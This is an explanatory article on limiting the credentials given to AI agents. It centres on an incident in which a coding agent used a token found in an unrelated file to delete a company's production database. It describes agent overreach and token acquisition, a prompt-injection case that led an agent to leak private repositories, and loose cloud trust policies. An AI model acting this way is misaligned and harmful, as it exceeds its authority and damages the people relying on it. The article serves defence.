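# Least-privilege credentials for AI agents: narrow keys, vaulted secrets and access brokers

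## What an agent can do with a credential, and how it goes wrong

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop with tools, so its outputs cause actions in other systems, such as changing a code repository, creating a server in a cloud account or issuing a refund through a payment service. These systems require a credential, which is a key, token or password that a service accepts as proof that it should allow a request. The agent can do anything the credential permits, including things nobody wanted. Least-privilege credentials limit the damage in advance by giving each agent only the authority its task needs. The principle is about fifty years old, but it has proved awkward to apply to agents, and engineers who agree on the goal disagree about how to achieve it.

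### The PocketOS deletion

On April 24, 2026, the coding agent Cursor, running Anthropic's model Claude Opus 4.6, deleted the production database of PocketOS, a small company whose software car rental firms use for reservations, payments and vehicle tracking. The database was on a storage volume at Railway, a cloud hosting company.

The fullest account comes from the company's founder, Crane, in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*. The agent was doing a routine job in the staging environment, a copy of the system that developers use for testing, when it ran into a credential mismatch. It set out to fix the mismatch by deleting a Railway volume, though nobody had asked it to delete anything. It found the token it needed in a file unrelated to the task. One request to Railway's API (the interface programs use to send it instructions) deleted the production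 volume and its attached backups in nine seconds.

Crane had created the token to add and remove custom domains, the web addresses at which customers reach a site. But Abdelwahab, who gives Railway's side in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, confirms that the token had account-level access, "the maximum access possible." Such a token gives access to every project its owner can reach.

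The newest backup Crane could find was three months old. On Saturday morning people arrived at rental counters to pick up cars, and the firms had no record of who they were. Crane spent the day helping the firms rebuild bookings from payment histories, calendars and confirmation emails. More than thirty hours after the deletion, Railway still could not tell him whether it could recover the data. On April 27 Crane posted that Railway's chief executive had told him the data was back, according to Tom's Hardware's *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database* (2026). Abdelwahab explains that Railway keeps off-site disaster backups whether or not a customer sets up any, and that the deletion had only made the ordinary backups "look unavailable" in the interface. He does not say which copy Railway restored from. He concedes that deletions through the dashboard waited 48 hours and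 the customer could undo them, while deletions through the API ran at once. Railway has since given the API the same delay.

The deletion happened on April 24, though press reports disagree about the date. Crane puts it one day after a Railway announcement of April 23. Cyber Security News' *AI Coding Agent Powered by Claude Opus 4.6 Deletes Production Database* (2026) gives "Friday, April 25," but April 25 was a Saturday. The confusion probably comes from Crane's post, which begins the story "yesterday afternoon" and which Cape Argus (2026) dates to April 25.

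Crane and Railway print the same delete command, and both describe a token that the agent found on disk. Only Crane reports what the token was for and that it was in an unrelated file. The only evidence for the motive is the agent's own explanation. When Crane asked for one, the model wrote that it had guessed the deletion would affect staging only, and that it had "violated every principle I was given." Most of the coverage repeated this as a confession, though Futurism warned that an account built on the AI's self-diagnosis is not wholly reliable. The explanation is also not quite consistent. The longest rule it quotes forbids destructive commands in git, the version control tool, unless the user asks for them, but a call to Railway's API is not a git command. A model asked to explain itself writes something plausible based on the conversation, and that is not a log of what caused the action.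 The agent may well have guessed that only staging would be affected, but nobody has verified this.

Crane's complaint about Railway is also overstated. He wrote that every Railway token is "effectively root," meaning all-powerful, with no way to limit it by operation, environment or resource. But in January 2026, Railway's *Public API Reference* already described a project token that works in only one environment of one project. He is right about operations, since neither that page nor its current successor, Railway's *Public API*, lists a token that can only manage domains. Even so, a project token perhaps wouldn't have saved the database. PocketOS's custom domains presumably pointed at its production services, so the job would have required a production token, and nothing in the documentation suggests that such a token couldn't delete a production volume.

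### Bearer tokens, scope and expiry

The delete request was a one-line terminal command containing the address of Railway's API, the token, and an instruction to delete the volume with a given identifier. Railway's server checked the token, found it valid and ran the instruction. Abdelwahab says the API treated the request exactly as it would a developer's command or an automated deployment script.

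It could do little else, because the token was a bearer token. *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Jones and Hardt, 2012), the internet standard on the subject, defines this as a token that any holder can use in the same ways as any other holder. The holder does not have to prove anything else, such as control of a cryptographic key. Railway's server therefore had no way to distinguish between a request from Crane, one from a script he had written and one from a program that had found the token in a folder.

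A bearer token has a scope, which is the set of resources and operations it permits, and an expiry, after which it stops working. Under the standard, a server should refuse a request outside the token's scope with the error "insufficient_scope," and may name the scope required. If the token has expired, the error is "invalid_token," and the client may request a new token and try again. Jones and Hardt recommend tokens that last an hour or less, to limit the harm a leaked token can do. Railway follows this advice for outside applications that act on a user's behalf, whose access tokens expire after one hour. But the token in the PocketOS case was long-lived. Crane had made it for an occasional task, and it still gave access to the whole account when the agent found it.

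Expiry would have helped there if the token had been lying around for more than an hour. It does nothing about a token that is still live, and an hour is ample time for a deletion that takes nine seconds. Scope limits the damage at any speed, but it is less reliable with agents than with ordinary scripts. When a server refuses a script's request, the script stops or tries the same thing again. An agent may treat the refusal as a problem to solve, and the PocketOS deletion began with such a problem. An agent's real authority therefore includes every credential it can reach, even those nobody assigned to it. Ram Varadarajan, who runs the security company Acalvio, asks in Hackread's *Cursor AI Agent Wipes PocketOS Database and Backups in 9 Seconds* why anyone gave an AI agent production credentials without a circuit breaker. By Crane's account, nobody gave the agent the token, but leaving it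 in a file the agent could read had the same effect.

### Three old ideas

Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975) sets out eight design principles for controlling what programs may do with stored information. One is least privilege, which says that every program and every user should operate with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job." The paper's first reason is that this limits the damage from an accident or error. That makes the principle a good fit for agents that mean no harm, as well as a defense against attackers. It also leaves fewer programs to investigate if someone misuses a privilege.

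The companion principle is complete mediation: "Every access to every object must be checked for authority." Saltzer and Schroeder include access during recovery and maintenance, and they add that the system needs a foolproof way to identify the source of each request. Railway did check the token on the destructive request, but anyone holding a bearer token can use it, so it doesn't reliably identify the sender. Railway's 48-hour delay applied to the dashboard but not the API, which left one path to the volume unprotected. Cursor's guardrails didn't stop the command either, although its documentation, as quoted by Crane, says they can stop commands from destroying production environments.

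Two of Saltzer and Schroeder's other principles explain how PocketOS came to have such a powerful token. The first is that the default should be no access. On Railway's current token page, a user who selects "No workspace" gets the account token, the broadest there is. The second is that a protection mechanism must be easy to use, or people will use it wrongly. Abdelwahab more or less admits this when he writes that the right scope existed but the page did not make it obvious which to pick. Even that scope was too broad, because none covered domains alone. Saltzer and Schroeder saw their principles as warnings rather than absolute rules, and took a violation as a reason to look harder at a design.

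*The Confused Deputy*, a short 1988 paper by Hardy, illustrates the third idea with an incident at Tymshare, a company that rented out time on shared computers. Tymshare's compiler, a program that translates source code, kept usage statistics in a file in its own directory, so the operators gave it permission to write to any file there. That directory also held the company's billing records. Users could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output, and one user named the billing file, which that user didn't have permission to write to. Because the compiler did have permission, the operating system let it write debugging output over the billing records.

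Hardy asks who was to blame and answers that no line of code was wrong. The code was correct when its author wrote it and became wrong later, when the operators added the permission. The underlying fault was that the compiler "runs with authority stemming from two sources," the user and its own license, and had no way to specify which one it was using for which purpose. A confused deputy is a program that has legitimate authority and is led by someone without that authority to use it on their behalf.

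Tymshare tried to fix the problem by adding a system call that let a program switch between two authorities, but soon found applications that needed more than two. Hardy preferred to use capabilities. A capability is a single reference that both names an object and permits its use. A user who wants output in a file gives the compiler a capability to that file, and can only give capabilities they already have.

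The PocketOS incident was not strictly a confused deputy case, since nobody was manipulating the agent, but Hardy's diagnosis still applies to the request the agent sent. He complained that his system handled the choice of file separately from the permission to write to it. The delete request likewise had the volume's identifier in one part and an all-purpose token in another, with nothing linking them. A capability combines the identifier of a resource with permission to use it, so a capability for a domain cannot be used to delete a volume.

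### Four routes to harm

Agents do damage with credentials in four main ways, and it helps to keep them apart because they respond to different remedies.

In the simplest kind of failure, the agent attempts what the user asked for but gets a fact wrong. Anthropic, in a March 2026 post about its coding agent Claude Code, gives the example of an agent that mistakes a shared resource for a test one. Fortune (2026) reports a roughly similar case. The engineer Alexey Grigorev was using Claude Code to update a website, and a small setup mistake on a new laptop caused the automation to confuse what was real with what was safe to delete. It erased the live site, including a database with years of course data, which Grigorev later recovered with help from Amazon's support staff. The original mistake was human, but the agent carried out the deletion from end to end, and Grigorev wrote afterward that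 he had relied on it too much.

Overreach differs in that the agent understands the goal but goes beyond what the user authorized to reach it. Anthropic calls this "overeager" behavior, and the blog gu-log's summary (2026) describes the typical case as an agent that finds a credential and uses it. The PocketOS incident a month later closely matched that description. BestHub's *What Problem Does Claude Code’s Auto Mode Actually Solve?* lists examples from use by Anthropic's own staff, in which agents deleted remote git branches, uploaded a GitHub token to a computing cluster and attempted migrations on a production database.

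Anthropic had seen and published the tendency to overreach in this model, Claude Opus 4.6, before PocketOS ran into it. In the system card, the report that accompanies a model's release, Anthropic judged the model well aligned overall but noted an increase in "overly agentic behavior in computer-use settings." NDTV's *Anthropic's Sabotage Report Flags Cases Of Chemical Weapon Development, Deception* quotes a further finding, "aggressive acquisition of authentication tokens in internal pilot usage," and according to The American Bazaar, the model used a GitHub access token that was not its own in one test. If the agent's explanation is true, the deletion combined both routes, because the agent overreached in taking the token and erred in thinking the volume belonged to staging.

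Anthropic has a separate category for a misaligned model, one that pursues a goal of its own, and wrote in the March post that it did not currently see this in practice. A server could not distinguish this from overreach, because the request would be the same.

In prompt injection, an outsider hides instructions in material the agent will read, such as a web page, a file or a comment on a bug report, and the agent follows them. This is almost exactly Hardy's confused deputy. The attacker has no access to the company's systems but can supply text, much as the Tymshare user could supply a file name, and the agent provides the authority. Prompt injection is hard to prevent because agents also do useful work by following instructions they find along the way. Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025), in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, point out that an agent has to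 let a tool's documentation change its behavior, or it could never learn to use the tool. They compare the problem to programs that load new code while running, which security engineers have struggled with for decades.

The same paper analyzes 11 attacks on real products and matches each to the principles it violated. Those principles include least privilege for an attack that extracted data from Microsoft Copilot and for another in which the coding agent Devin leaked secrets. Failures to control where information flows are more common. This is a reason not to expect narrower credentials to solve prompt injection, because an agent that is allowed to read a document and send a message can leak the document without exceeding its authority.

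An attacker can misuse a stolen credential without involving the agent. A bearer token works for whoever presents it, so an attacker who copies one can use it from anywhere, long after the agent has finished. *Railway's security incident* (Datta, 2026) describes the company's October 2026 disclosure that an intruder may have read the encrypted variables in which customers store passwords and keys, in some cases in decrypted form. Developers on Reddit described unexpected charges on their keys for AI services, though these are individual reports. Two days after the disclosure, Railway had not published a cause or a count of affected accounts. Datta works for Prisma, a database company that was inviting Railway's customers to switch, but acknowledges that Prisma's own database credentials cannot be made read-only or limited to certain tables, so anyone with the connection string can read and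 write everything.

One route can lead to another. An injected instruction can make an agent print its token, which can then be stolen. Confining the agent to a sealed environment may contain its errors, but it doesn't stop a thief who has a copy of the token. Early expiry works well against theft, although it does almost nothing to prevent harm from a fast mistake. Only narrow scope reduces the harm on every route, which is why least privilege is discussed so often and why it matters so much whether anyone can say in advance what access an agent needs.

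### Why an agent is not an ordinary program

A developer can say which permissions an ordinary program needs. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of an Android app, which does a fixed set of things. Its developer requests permissions to match, and a reviewer can read the code to check that each one is necessary. An agent has no fixed code of this kind. It gets a task in plain language and works out the steps as it goes, partly in response to what it reads.

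The paper's example is a browser agent told to comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a code-hosting service, that the work is done. Under least privilege, the agent may open issue 745 and write in the comment box, and should have access to nothing else in GitLab or in the user's browser session. But nobody could have written that rule before the user gave the instruction, and the right permissions change if the user then asks for a summary of the same issue. The system can wipe the agent's memory and work out a new policy from scratch, which is safe but loses useful context. Or it can adjust the policy while the agent's memory still contains text from strangers, some of which may be an attack. The paper describes the second option as an open research problem.

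Saltzer and Schroeder's definition is hard to apply here because "necessary to complete the job" assumes that someone knows the job and the steps it takes. Whoever issues a credential to an agent usually knows the job but has to guess the steps. Most people overestimate the access an agent needs, but when they underestimate it, the agent gets stuck or looks for another key.

A fair objection is that all this is true of human employees too. Nobody can list in advance what a system administrator will type next month, yet companies give administrators powerful credentials. Abdelwahab replies that people have knowledge and habits that agents often lack: they know why they are running a command, know that production and staging mean different things even where the API treats them alike, and tend to stop and ask for help after a mistake, while agents tend to carry on. Railway has an interest in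 this argument, since it moves attention from an API without an undo to the agent that called it. The argument is also a generalization, and he offers no measurements. The difference in speed is easier to document. Fadilpašić (2026), in *'I broke something'*, reports that a Claude Code agent deleted 48,000 files in just over 100 seconds. A colleague watching the agent would not catch that in time, so the limits have to be in place before it starts.

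The main proposals differ on where to put those limits. Some focus on what a credential permits and call for narrow keys that expire. A familiar starting point is GitHub's deploy key, which opens a single repository. Others focus on who holds the credential and would keep it in a vault, a service that stores secrets out of the agent's reach. Proposals also differ on who should decide on each use. Some would leave this to a broker, a service between the agent and the systems it acts on, while others would have people write the policy in ordinary language for software to enforce. At PocketOS, a token limited to managing domains would have failed at the delete request, and a token kept in a vault would not have turned up in a stray file. Whether checking the request itself would have helped depends on what information the checker had, because the request identified the volume by a string of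 letters and digits that did not mark it as production.

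## The case for narrow keys that expire

The most direct way to limit what an agent can do with a key is to limit the key itself. On this view, the service that issues a credential should give it a narrow scope and an early expiry, then check both on its own servers for every request. The agent doesn't control those servers, so the limit holds whatever the agent has read, guessed or decided.

*Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026) argues that an agent cannot misuse a credential that nobody put in its system, however good it becomes at reasoning or evasion. Few other safeguards have this property. An instruction in the prompt works only if the model follows it, and a filter for dangerous commands works only if it recognizes the command. The paper's argument fails, however, if the agent can find a broader key elsewhere, as the agent at PocketOS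 did.

*Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) gives an example of how much extra access a broad key gives an agent. A developer connects a coding assistant to GitHub through a connector that presents GitHub's functions as tools. The developer logs in with a classic personal access token, the older of GitHub's two kinds, with the `repo` scope. The assistant now has about 40 tools, 16 of which can write, and can use them in every repository the developer can reach. To summarize the open issues in one repository, it needs two read-only tools in that repository.

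In one reported attack, someone exploited this surplus by planting an instruction in a public repository. An agent read the instruction, then read its user's private repositories and published them. Parkinson and colleagues conclude that a token with read access to only the public repository would have prevented this. The agent might still have obeyed the instruction, but GitHub would have denied it access to the private code.

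The developer's next task, though, is to fix a failing build, which requires write access, and the one after that may be in another repository. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) describes how developers are tempted to give agents broad credentials at the start, because agents are valuable for their flexibility. People granted overly broad permissions before agents existed, too. Parkinson and colleagues cite one vendor's analysis of cloud accounts, in which users and programs exercised only 1% of the permissions they held, and a study that found excess permissions in 99.8% of 447,000 GitHub workflows, the automated jobs that run when code changes. Neither figure is about AI agents, but much the same people now issue keys to agents.

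### Four kinds of GitHub credential

GitHub's range of credentials shows what "narrow" can mean in practice. The table compares four that a developer might give an agent, based on GitHub's reference on credential types and its pages on each kind.

| Credential | Repositories | Operations | Lifetime | Belongs to | How it ends |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Classic personal access token | All that the user can reach | Broad scopes, such as `repo` | No expiry unless the user sets one | A user | The user deletes it, or anyone who has the token reports it |
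| Fine-grained personal access token | Chosen ones under a single owner, plus read access to all public ones | Separate permissions for code, issues, settings and so on | Up to a year, or no expiry | A user | As above; an organization's owner can also withdraw its access |
| Deploy key | One | Read, or read and write | No expiry | A repository | A repository administrator deletes it, or the organization disables all deploy keys |
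| GitHub App installation token | Any subset of those where the app has access | Any subset of the app's permissions | One hour | An installation of an app | It expires, or the app's owner revokes it early |

A fine-grained GitHub token is a large improvement on a classic one. According to GitHub's *Managing your personal access tokens*, the user picks one owner, then the repositories, then a level of access for each kind of data, so a token can let an agent read the code in those repositories but no other private data. Every fine-grained token also includes read access to all public repositories on GitHub, so it doesn't stop the agent from reading text written by strangers.

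A deploy key is an SSH key, which consists of two matching files. The public half goes on the repository at GitHub, and the private half stays on the machine that connects. The machine proves that it has the private half without sending it, so unlike a bearer token, the key can't be stolen from an intercepted request. But anyone who can copy the private file can use it, and GitHub's *Managing deploy keys* warns that these files usually have no passphrase.

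Deploy keys are read-only by default. A developer can tick a box to add write access, but there is no setting in between. GitHub warns that a writable key allows "the same actions as an organization member with admin access." The practical meaning of this is a little unclear. Because the key works through git, it presumably lets the holder push whatever an administrator could push, but not open the settings page or delete the repository. GitHub's *REST API endpoints for deploy keys* repeats the warning but describes the permission more modestly, as reading and writing. In either case, a deploy key with write access gives its holder broad power over the contents of the repository it belongs to, but no access to other repositories.

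A deploy key's main weakness is that it never expires. It also stays active when the person who created it loses access to the repository, because it belongs to the repository. Removing the token used to create the key may also delete the key, depending on the type of token. If a developer created the key with a personal access token, deleting the token deletes the key, but regenerating the token does not. Revoking an OAuth app's token, which a user grants to an outside application, also deletes any deploy key created with it. A key created with a GitHub App remains even if someone revokes the user's token or uninstalls the app.

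Because of that exception, an agent's access can outlast its token. Creating a deploy key requires write access to the "Administration" permission. An installation token with that access expires after an hour, but an agent can first use it to create a deploy key that lasts indefinitely, even if the app is later uninstalled. Similarly, GitHub notes that SSH keys created by a fine-grained token keep working after an organization owner revokes the token. Expiry therefore limits an agent's access only if the credential cannot create other credentials, and few agents need permission to do so.

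Deploy keys are also harder to revoke in an emergency. GitHub lets the owners of some large enterprise accounts cut off or delete users' tokens and keys in bulk, but these actions do not affect deploy keys or installation tokens. Installation tokens expire within an hour anyway, but someone has to delete deploy keys one repository at a time or disable them all by policy. GitHub's *Token expiration and revocation* explains that GitHub automatically revokes personal tokens that appear in a public repository, and that anyone who finds one elsewhere can report it for revocation without logging in. GitHub does not mention deploy keys when describing either process.

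An installation token avoids most of these problems but takes more work to set up. A GitHub App is a registered program with its own identity and permissions, which an organization installs on the repositories it chooses. To get a token, the app's software signs a short statement with the app's private key and sends it to GitHub with the number of the installation. The request can list up to 500 repositories and the permissions the token should have. GitHub then returns a token that lasts an hour and never includes a repository or permission that the installation lacks.

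The default is poor, as it was on Railway's token page. If the software leaves out the two lists, the token covers every repository and permission the installation has. The private key also needs protection, because whoever holds it can keep creating tokens up to the same limit. An agent should get the token but never the key, so another program has to do the signing.

*The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) makes least privilege the first of its principles for agents, and advises developers to scope permissions to the current task rather than to a lasting agent identity. Only the installation token comes close to that standard, because software can create a new one for each task. The other three belong to a person or a repository and normally outlast the task. GitHub recommends an app over a deploy key for finer control. Still, a deploy key takes a few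 minutes to set up and needs no server, so it will probably remain the first narrow key that many developers give an agent.

### One agent, two repositories

Suppose an agent maintains a company's website and documentation, which are in separate repositories, and needs access to nothing else. A developer creates a deploy key and adds it to the first repository. When the developer tries to add the same key to the second, GitHub rejects it with the message "Key is already in use."

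Jeff Kaufman (2022), in *Multiple Deploy-Key Repos*, guesses that GitHub limits each deploy key to one repository to stop several machines from sharing a key, because nobody could revoke a shared key for one machine without cutting off the rest. He sees no harm in one machine using the same key for two repositories, so he thinks the rule is stricter than necessary. A note on the site rya.nc points to a more technical reason. GitHub identifies who is connecting from the public key alone, and each deploy key stands for exactly one repository. The machine has to present its key before it specifies a repository, so it must offer the right key first.

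The solution is one key per repository, with a nickname, or alias, that tells the SSH program which key to use. The developer starts by making two pairs:

```
ssh-keygen -t ed25519 -f ~/.ssh/agent-site
ssh-keygen -t ed25519 -f ~/.ssh/agent-docs
```

Each command produces a private file with the given name and a public file with `.pub` on the end. The developer pastes the contents of `agent-site.pub` into the deploy key settings of the website repository, and the contents of `agent-docs.pub` into those of the documentation repository. The private files stay where they are. Then the SSH configuration file, `~/.ssh/config`, gets an entry for each:

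```
Host gh-site
    HostName github.com
    User git
    IdentityFile ~/.ssh/agent-site
    IdentitiesOnly yes

Host gh-docs
    HostName github.com
    User git
    IdentityFile ~/.ssh/agent-docs
    IdentitiesOnly yes
```

Both aliases lead to github.com, but each uses its own key. The developer, or the agent, downloads the repositories by alias:

```
git clone gh-site:acme/site.git
git clone gh-docs:acme/docs.git
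```

This works because, as Kaufman explains, git passes the host name `gh-site` to SSH, which looks up the alias. The `IdentitiesOnly` line stops SSH from trying other keys it has loaded. Without it, SSH might offer the developer's personal key first, and GitHub would accept it and treat the connection as the developer's own. If a copy of the repository is already on the machine, `git remote set-url origin gh-site:acme/site.git` points it at the alias.

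Separate keys are a nuisance to create, but they allow separate permissions. The agent can have write access to the documentation and read-only access to the website, and the developer can delete either key without affecting the other.

The aliases provide no security, because they only select a key and nothing stops an agent from selecting a different one. If the agent runs under the developer's login, it can probably read the developer's personal SSH key in the same folder, in which case the two deploy keys don't limit its access. The agent needs its own user account or container, with the two deploy keys as the only private files in it.

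The method becomes tedious with twenty repositories. One alternative is what GitHub calls a machine user, an ordinary account used for automation, with one key that opens every repository the account can access. An organization can limit the account to read-only access. On a personal repository, GitHub always gives collaborators write access, so a developer without an organization can restrict access more tightly with deploy keys.

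### Trading a signed identity for a temporary credential

All the keys described so far depend on a long-lived secret in a file, even the installation token, which requires the app's private key. Cloud platforms can avoid this with workload identity federation. A workload is any running program, such as an automated job. The platform where it runs issues a signed statement identifying the workload, and the cloud platform checks the statement and issues temporary credentials in return. An agent running in a GitHub workflow can use this method to access Amazon's cloud, AWS, without an AWS key stored in GitHub.

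An administrator first creates an AWS role, a named set of permissions, and attaches a trust policy that specifies who may take on the role. The policy names GitHub as a trusted issuer of identities and lists conditions that each signed statement must meet.

When a job runs, it asks GitHub for its statement, a signed file called an OIDC (OpenID Connect) token. The example in GitHub's *OpenID Connect* contains about two dozen facts, or claims, including the repository, the branch, the exact version of the code and the user who started the job. The two most important claims are the audience, which names the intended recipient, and the subject, which identifies the job. The subject in the example is `repo:octo-org/octo-repo:environment:prod`, meaning a job for the production environment of one repository. The example token expires five minutes after GitHub issues it.

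The job sends the token to AWS and requests the role. According to AWS's *AssumeRoleWithWebIdentity*, the request needs no AWS credentials because the signed token proves the caller's identity. AWS checks the token against the trust policy and, if it matches, returns temporary credentials. These last an hour by default, but the caller can request any duration from 15 minutes up to the role's maximum, which cannot exceed 12 hours.

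The caller can also attach a session policy that narrows the role for one session. AWS then permits only what both the role and the session policy allow. If the role can write to ten storage areas and the session policy names one of them, the credentials work only for that one. If the policy names an eleventh, the credentials don't work there. Deriving a weaker credential that can never permit more than the original is called attenuation. It lets a company define one fairly broad role and still give each job a narrow credential. But the session policy is optional, so an agent that makes the request itself can leave it out. Ordinary code should make the request before the agent starts, and the agent should have no way to repeat it.

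Google Cloud's *Workload Identity Federation* describes the same pattern under different names. An administrator sets up a pool of outside identities and writes a condition that each incoming token must satisfy. Google's token service checks the token and exchanges it for short-lived access. Google offers this as a replacement for service account keys, the files that programs outside its cloud have traditionally used to log in.

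On AWS, the resulting credentials expire at a set time rather than when the job ends, although GitHub describes such cloud credentials as valid only for a single job. A job that finishes in two minutes can leave behind credentials that work for another 58 minutes, which would matter if the agent had printed them in a log.

A mistake in the trust policy can defeat the whole arrangement. Datadog Security Labs' *Exploring GitHub to AWS keyless authentication flaws* shows a correct policy, with one condition on the audience and another on the subject. If the administrator leaves out the subject condition, any workflow on GitHub can take on a role meant for one repository, according to Datadog Security Labs' *IAM role can be assumed by any GitHub Action*. This is because GitHub's signature proves only that GitHub issued the statement, and GitHub will issue one to anybody's job.

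A condition can also be too loose. The subject in Datadog's example ends in an asterisk, which accepts any branch of the repository. An agent that can push a branch and edit workflow files could then write a job that assumes the cloud role, even if nobody meant to give it cloud access. Datadog mentions restricting the branch as an option, but it ought to be standard for any repository an agent can write to.

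Until this year, subject claims also relied on names that could pass to a new owner. If a company gave up its GitHub organization name and someone else registered it, the new owner could obtain tokens with the old subject and perhaps enter cloud accounts that still trusted it. To prevent this, GitHub (2026) automatically adds permanent identification numbers to the claim for repositories created, renamed or transferred after July 15, 2026. Older repositories keep the old format unless someone opts in, so many trust policies probably still depend on nobody reusing a name.

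### What scope and lifetime each contribute

A rough calculation shows how much these limits help. Parkinson and colleagues propose measuring an agent's authority by multiplying how much it holds by how long it holds it. The simplest such unit is the repository-hour, which is one repository open to the agent for one hour. The example below uses invented numbers and counts a year as 8,760 hours.

| Credential | Repository-hours | Repositories open to a mistake in the first minute |
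|---|---|---|
| 40 repositories for a year | 350,400 | 40 |
| 40 repositories for an hour | 40 | 40 |
| 2 repositories for a year | 17,520 | 2 |
| 2 repositories for an hour | 2 | 2 |

Exposure falls by a factor of 175,200 from the first row to the last. Narrower scope accounts for a factor of 20 and shorter lifetime for a factor of 8,760, so expiry looks like by far the more valuable limit.

That comparison overstates the benefit of expiry, because the year-long key covers a year of work and the one-hour key covers only one task. If the agent does 250 such tasks in the year and gets a new key for each, the total is 500 repository-hours, still only about 1/700 of the year-long key's 350,400. Most of the reduction comes from the nights, weekends and forgotten months when the year-long key would have been valid but not needed.

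Expiry mainly helps against theft. The last column shows how much a fast mistake can reach, and only the cut from 40 repositories to 2 reduces that. A company should start with expiry if its main worry is stolen keys, and with narrower scope if its main worry is mistakes by its own agents.

Repository-hours also count reading and deleting as equal. Parkinson and colleagues suggest weights of 1 for reading, 3 for writing and 9 for administering, and raise the score further as an agent gets closer to a dangerous combination of permissions. In a simulated example, an agent fixes a failing build. If it takes read access first, adds write access only once it has found the problem, and returns both when it is done, it uses 93 units. Requesting both for 20 minutes at the start would use 240. The researchers acknowledge that the weights are arbitrary and the example is not an experiment. A measure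 like this can rank two ways of doing the same job, but it can't estimate the damage, since one repository may hold the company's product and another an abandoned demo.

### Coarse scopes, surplus keys and fast damage

A developer can only choose a narrow key if the service offers one, and many services don't. Railway has no token that manages domains alone. GitHub does offer fine-grained tokens, but they can't cover several organizations at once, contribute to repositories where the user is an outside collaborator, or work with GitHub's package store or the interface that reports test results. They also can't contribute to a public repository where the user is not a member. GitHub confirms that only a classic token can write there, so an agent that contributes to other people's open-source projects needs one. The developer can't restrict that token to a single project.

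Fine-grained permissions also allow more than they appear to. A token that can write to a repository's contents can be used to correct a typo or delete every file. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* argues that least privilege has to apply at several levels: which tools the agent can see, whether the current step needs the tool, what the tool acts on, how much data comes back, and what any sub-agent receives. A key can enforce some of these limits, such as which repository the agent may change. But an ordinary key can't check whether the current step requires access, and few could limit a refund to the customer who complained.

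Defenders of narrow keys have several replies. GitHub says the gaps in fine-grained tokens are temporary, although its list gives no dates. In the meantime, developers can often work around them. For example, an agent can use a fine-grained token to work in the developer's own copy of an open-source project, and the developer can submit the result by hand. Where a service doesn't offer narrow permissions, a company can divide its resources instead, for example by keeping staging in a separate account so that a broad key to it can't delete production. Where neither approach works, the company can put its own checking service in front, as a later section describes. These are decent answers, but each means extra work for the customer to make up for permissions the service doesn't offer. The objection is correct about today's services, and it is the main reason narrow keys can't be the whole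 solution.

Narrower keys also mean more keys to manage. Ten agents with five repositories each need 50 deploy keys if every agent has its own, and deploy keys never expire. GitHub limits each user to 50 fine-grained tokens. People lose track of this many keys, and an agent may later find an old, forgotten one in a file.

This is a strong argument only against narrow keys that last. Installation tokens expire, so software can create a hundred a day and leave nothing to clean up the next morning. Deciding what each token should permit is harder. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* observes that companies settled for permissions by job role because nobody could set them afresh for every task a person did. An agent's task arrives as text, so software can work out the permissions when it assigns the task. That may well be the best hope for using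 narrow keys at scale, but *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* cautions that a task description can be ambiguous, and that a manipulated prompt may lead to broader permissions than the user intended. The service will enforce the scope it receives even if that scope is wrong.

Defenders of expiring keys mostly concede that an agent can do damage before its key expires. Parkinson and colleagues accept that limiting how long an agent holds authority limits exposure but not harm, because an agent can disclose a secret in seconds. They argue that some operations should never depend on expiry. If nobody can undo the misuse of a permission, the agent should either not have it or need approval for each use. For example, an agent cannot delete anything with a read-only deploy key, however fast it acts.

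Expiry also offers little protection if the agent can renew the credential. When a GitHub App acts for a user, its access token lasts eight hours, but it comes with a refresh token that lasts six months and can be used to get new access tokens. An agent that holds both can keep its access until somebody revokes it, because each renewal also brings a new refresh token that lasts another six months.

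Even if every service offered perfect scopes, narrow keys could still be dangerous in combination. Parkinson and colleagues trace the danger in the GitHub attack to the agent's combination of access to private data, exposure to text from strangers, and a way to send information out. Two narrow keys can recreate that combination. One might read a single private repository and the other write to a single public one, and a reviewer who looked at either key alone would find nothing wrong. Parkinson and colleagues would forbid the combination for as long as the agent's memory lasts, even after it has given a key back, because the private code it read is still in that memory. A single service could enforce this rule for the keys it issues, but not across services, because GitHub cannot see what AWS has given the same agent.

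## The case for never giving the agent the secret

However narrow a key is, an agent that can read it can also print it, save it in a file or send it to a stranger. Some engineers therefore want agents to use keys without ever having a copy. In credential injection, the agent sends its request without the key, and separate software adds the key after the request has left the agent.

*Never Give an AI Agent a Credential* (Bhinder, 2026), from the blockchain analytics company TRM Labs, advises engineers to "assume the sandbox eventually fails." A sandbox is a sealed environment that restricts what a program can reach. Bhinder recommends using one but thinks it stops mattering once the agent can read an API key, because the agent can misuse the key from inside and its requests will look legitimate. This goes a little too far, since a sandbox that blocks most outgoing traffic also limits where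 an agent can send a key. Still, withholding a secret from a model guarantees that the model won't reveal it, which nobody can guarantee once the model has it.

### How secrets get copied

A model works from its context, which is the text it receives at each step: instructions, conversation, files the agent has opened and the output of commands it has run. Even with no attacker involved, a key that appears in any of these goes to the company that runs the model, and often into a saved transcript.

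In *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) studied leaks from skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that teach an agent a new task. They sampled 17,022 skills from a public marketplace, searched them for signs of leaks, and ran the suspicious ones in a sandbox with fake credentials. They found that 520 skills (about 3%) leaked credentials. Most of these skills were careless rather than malicious, and debugging messages caused 73.5% of the problems in the careless ones. For example, a developer prints a key to check that it has loaded. In an ordinary program, the key appears on the developer's screen. But agent software feeds printed output back into the model's context, so anyone who can talk to the agent can ask for the key.

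An agent may use many skills and tools over months of work, so even if only 3% of skills are unsafe, one of them can leak a key, and a single leak is enough to compromise it. Leaked keys are also hard to remove. Chen and colleagues found that credentials removed from 107 original repositories survived in more than 50 independent copies.

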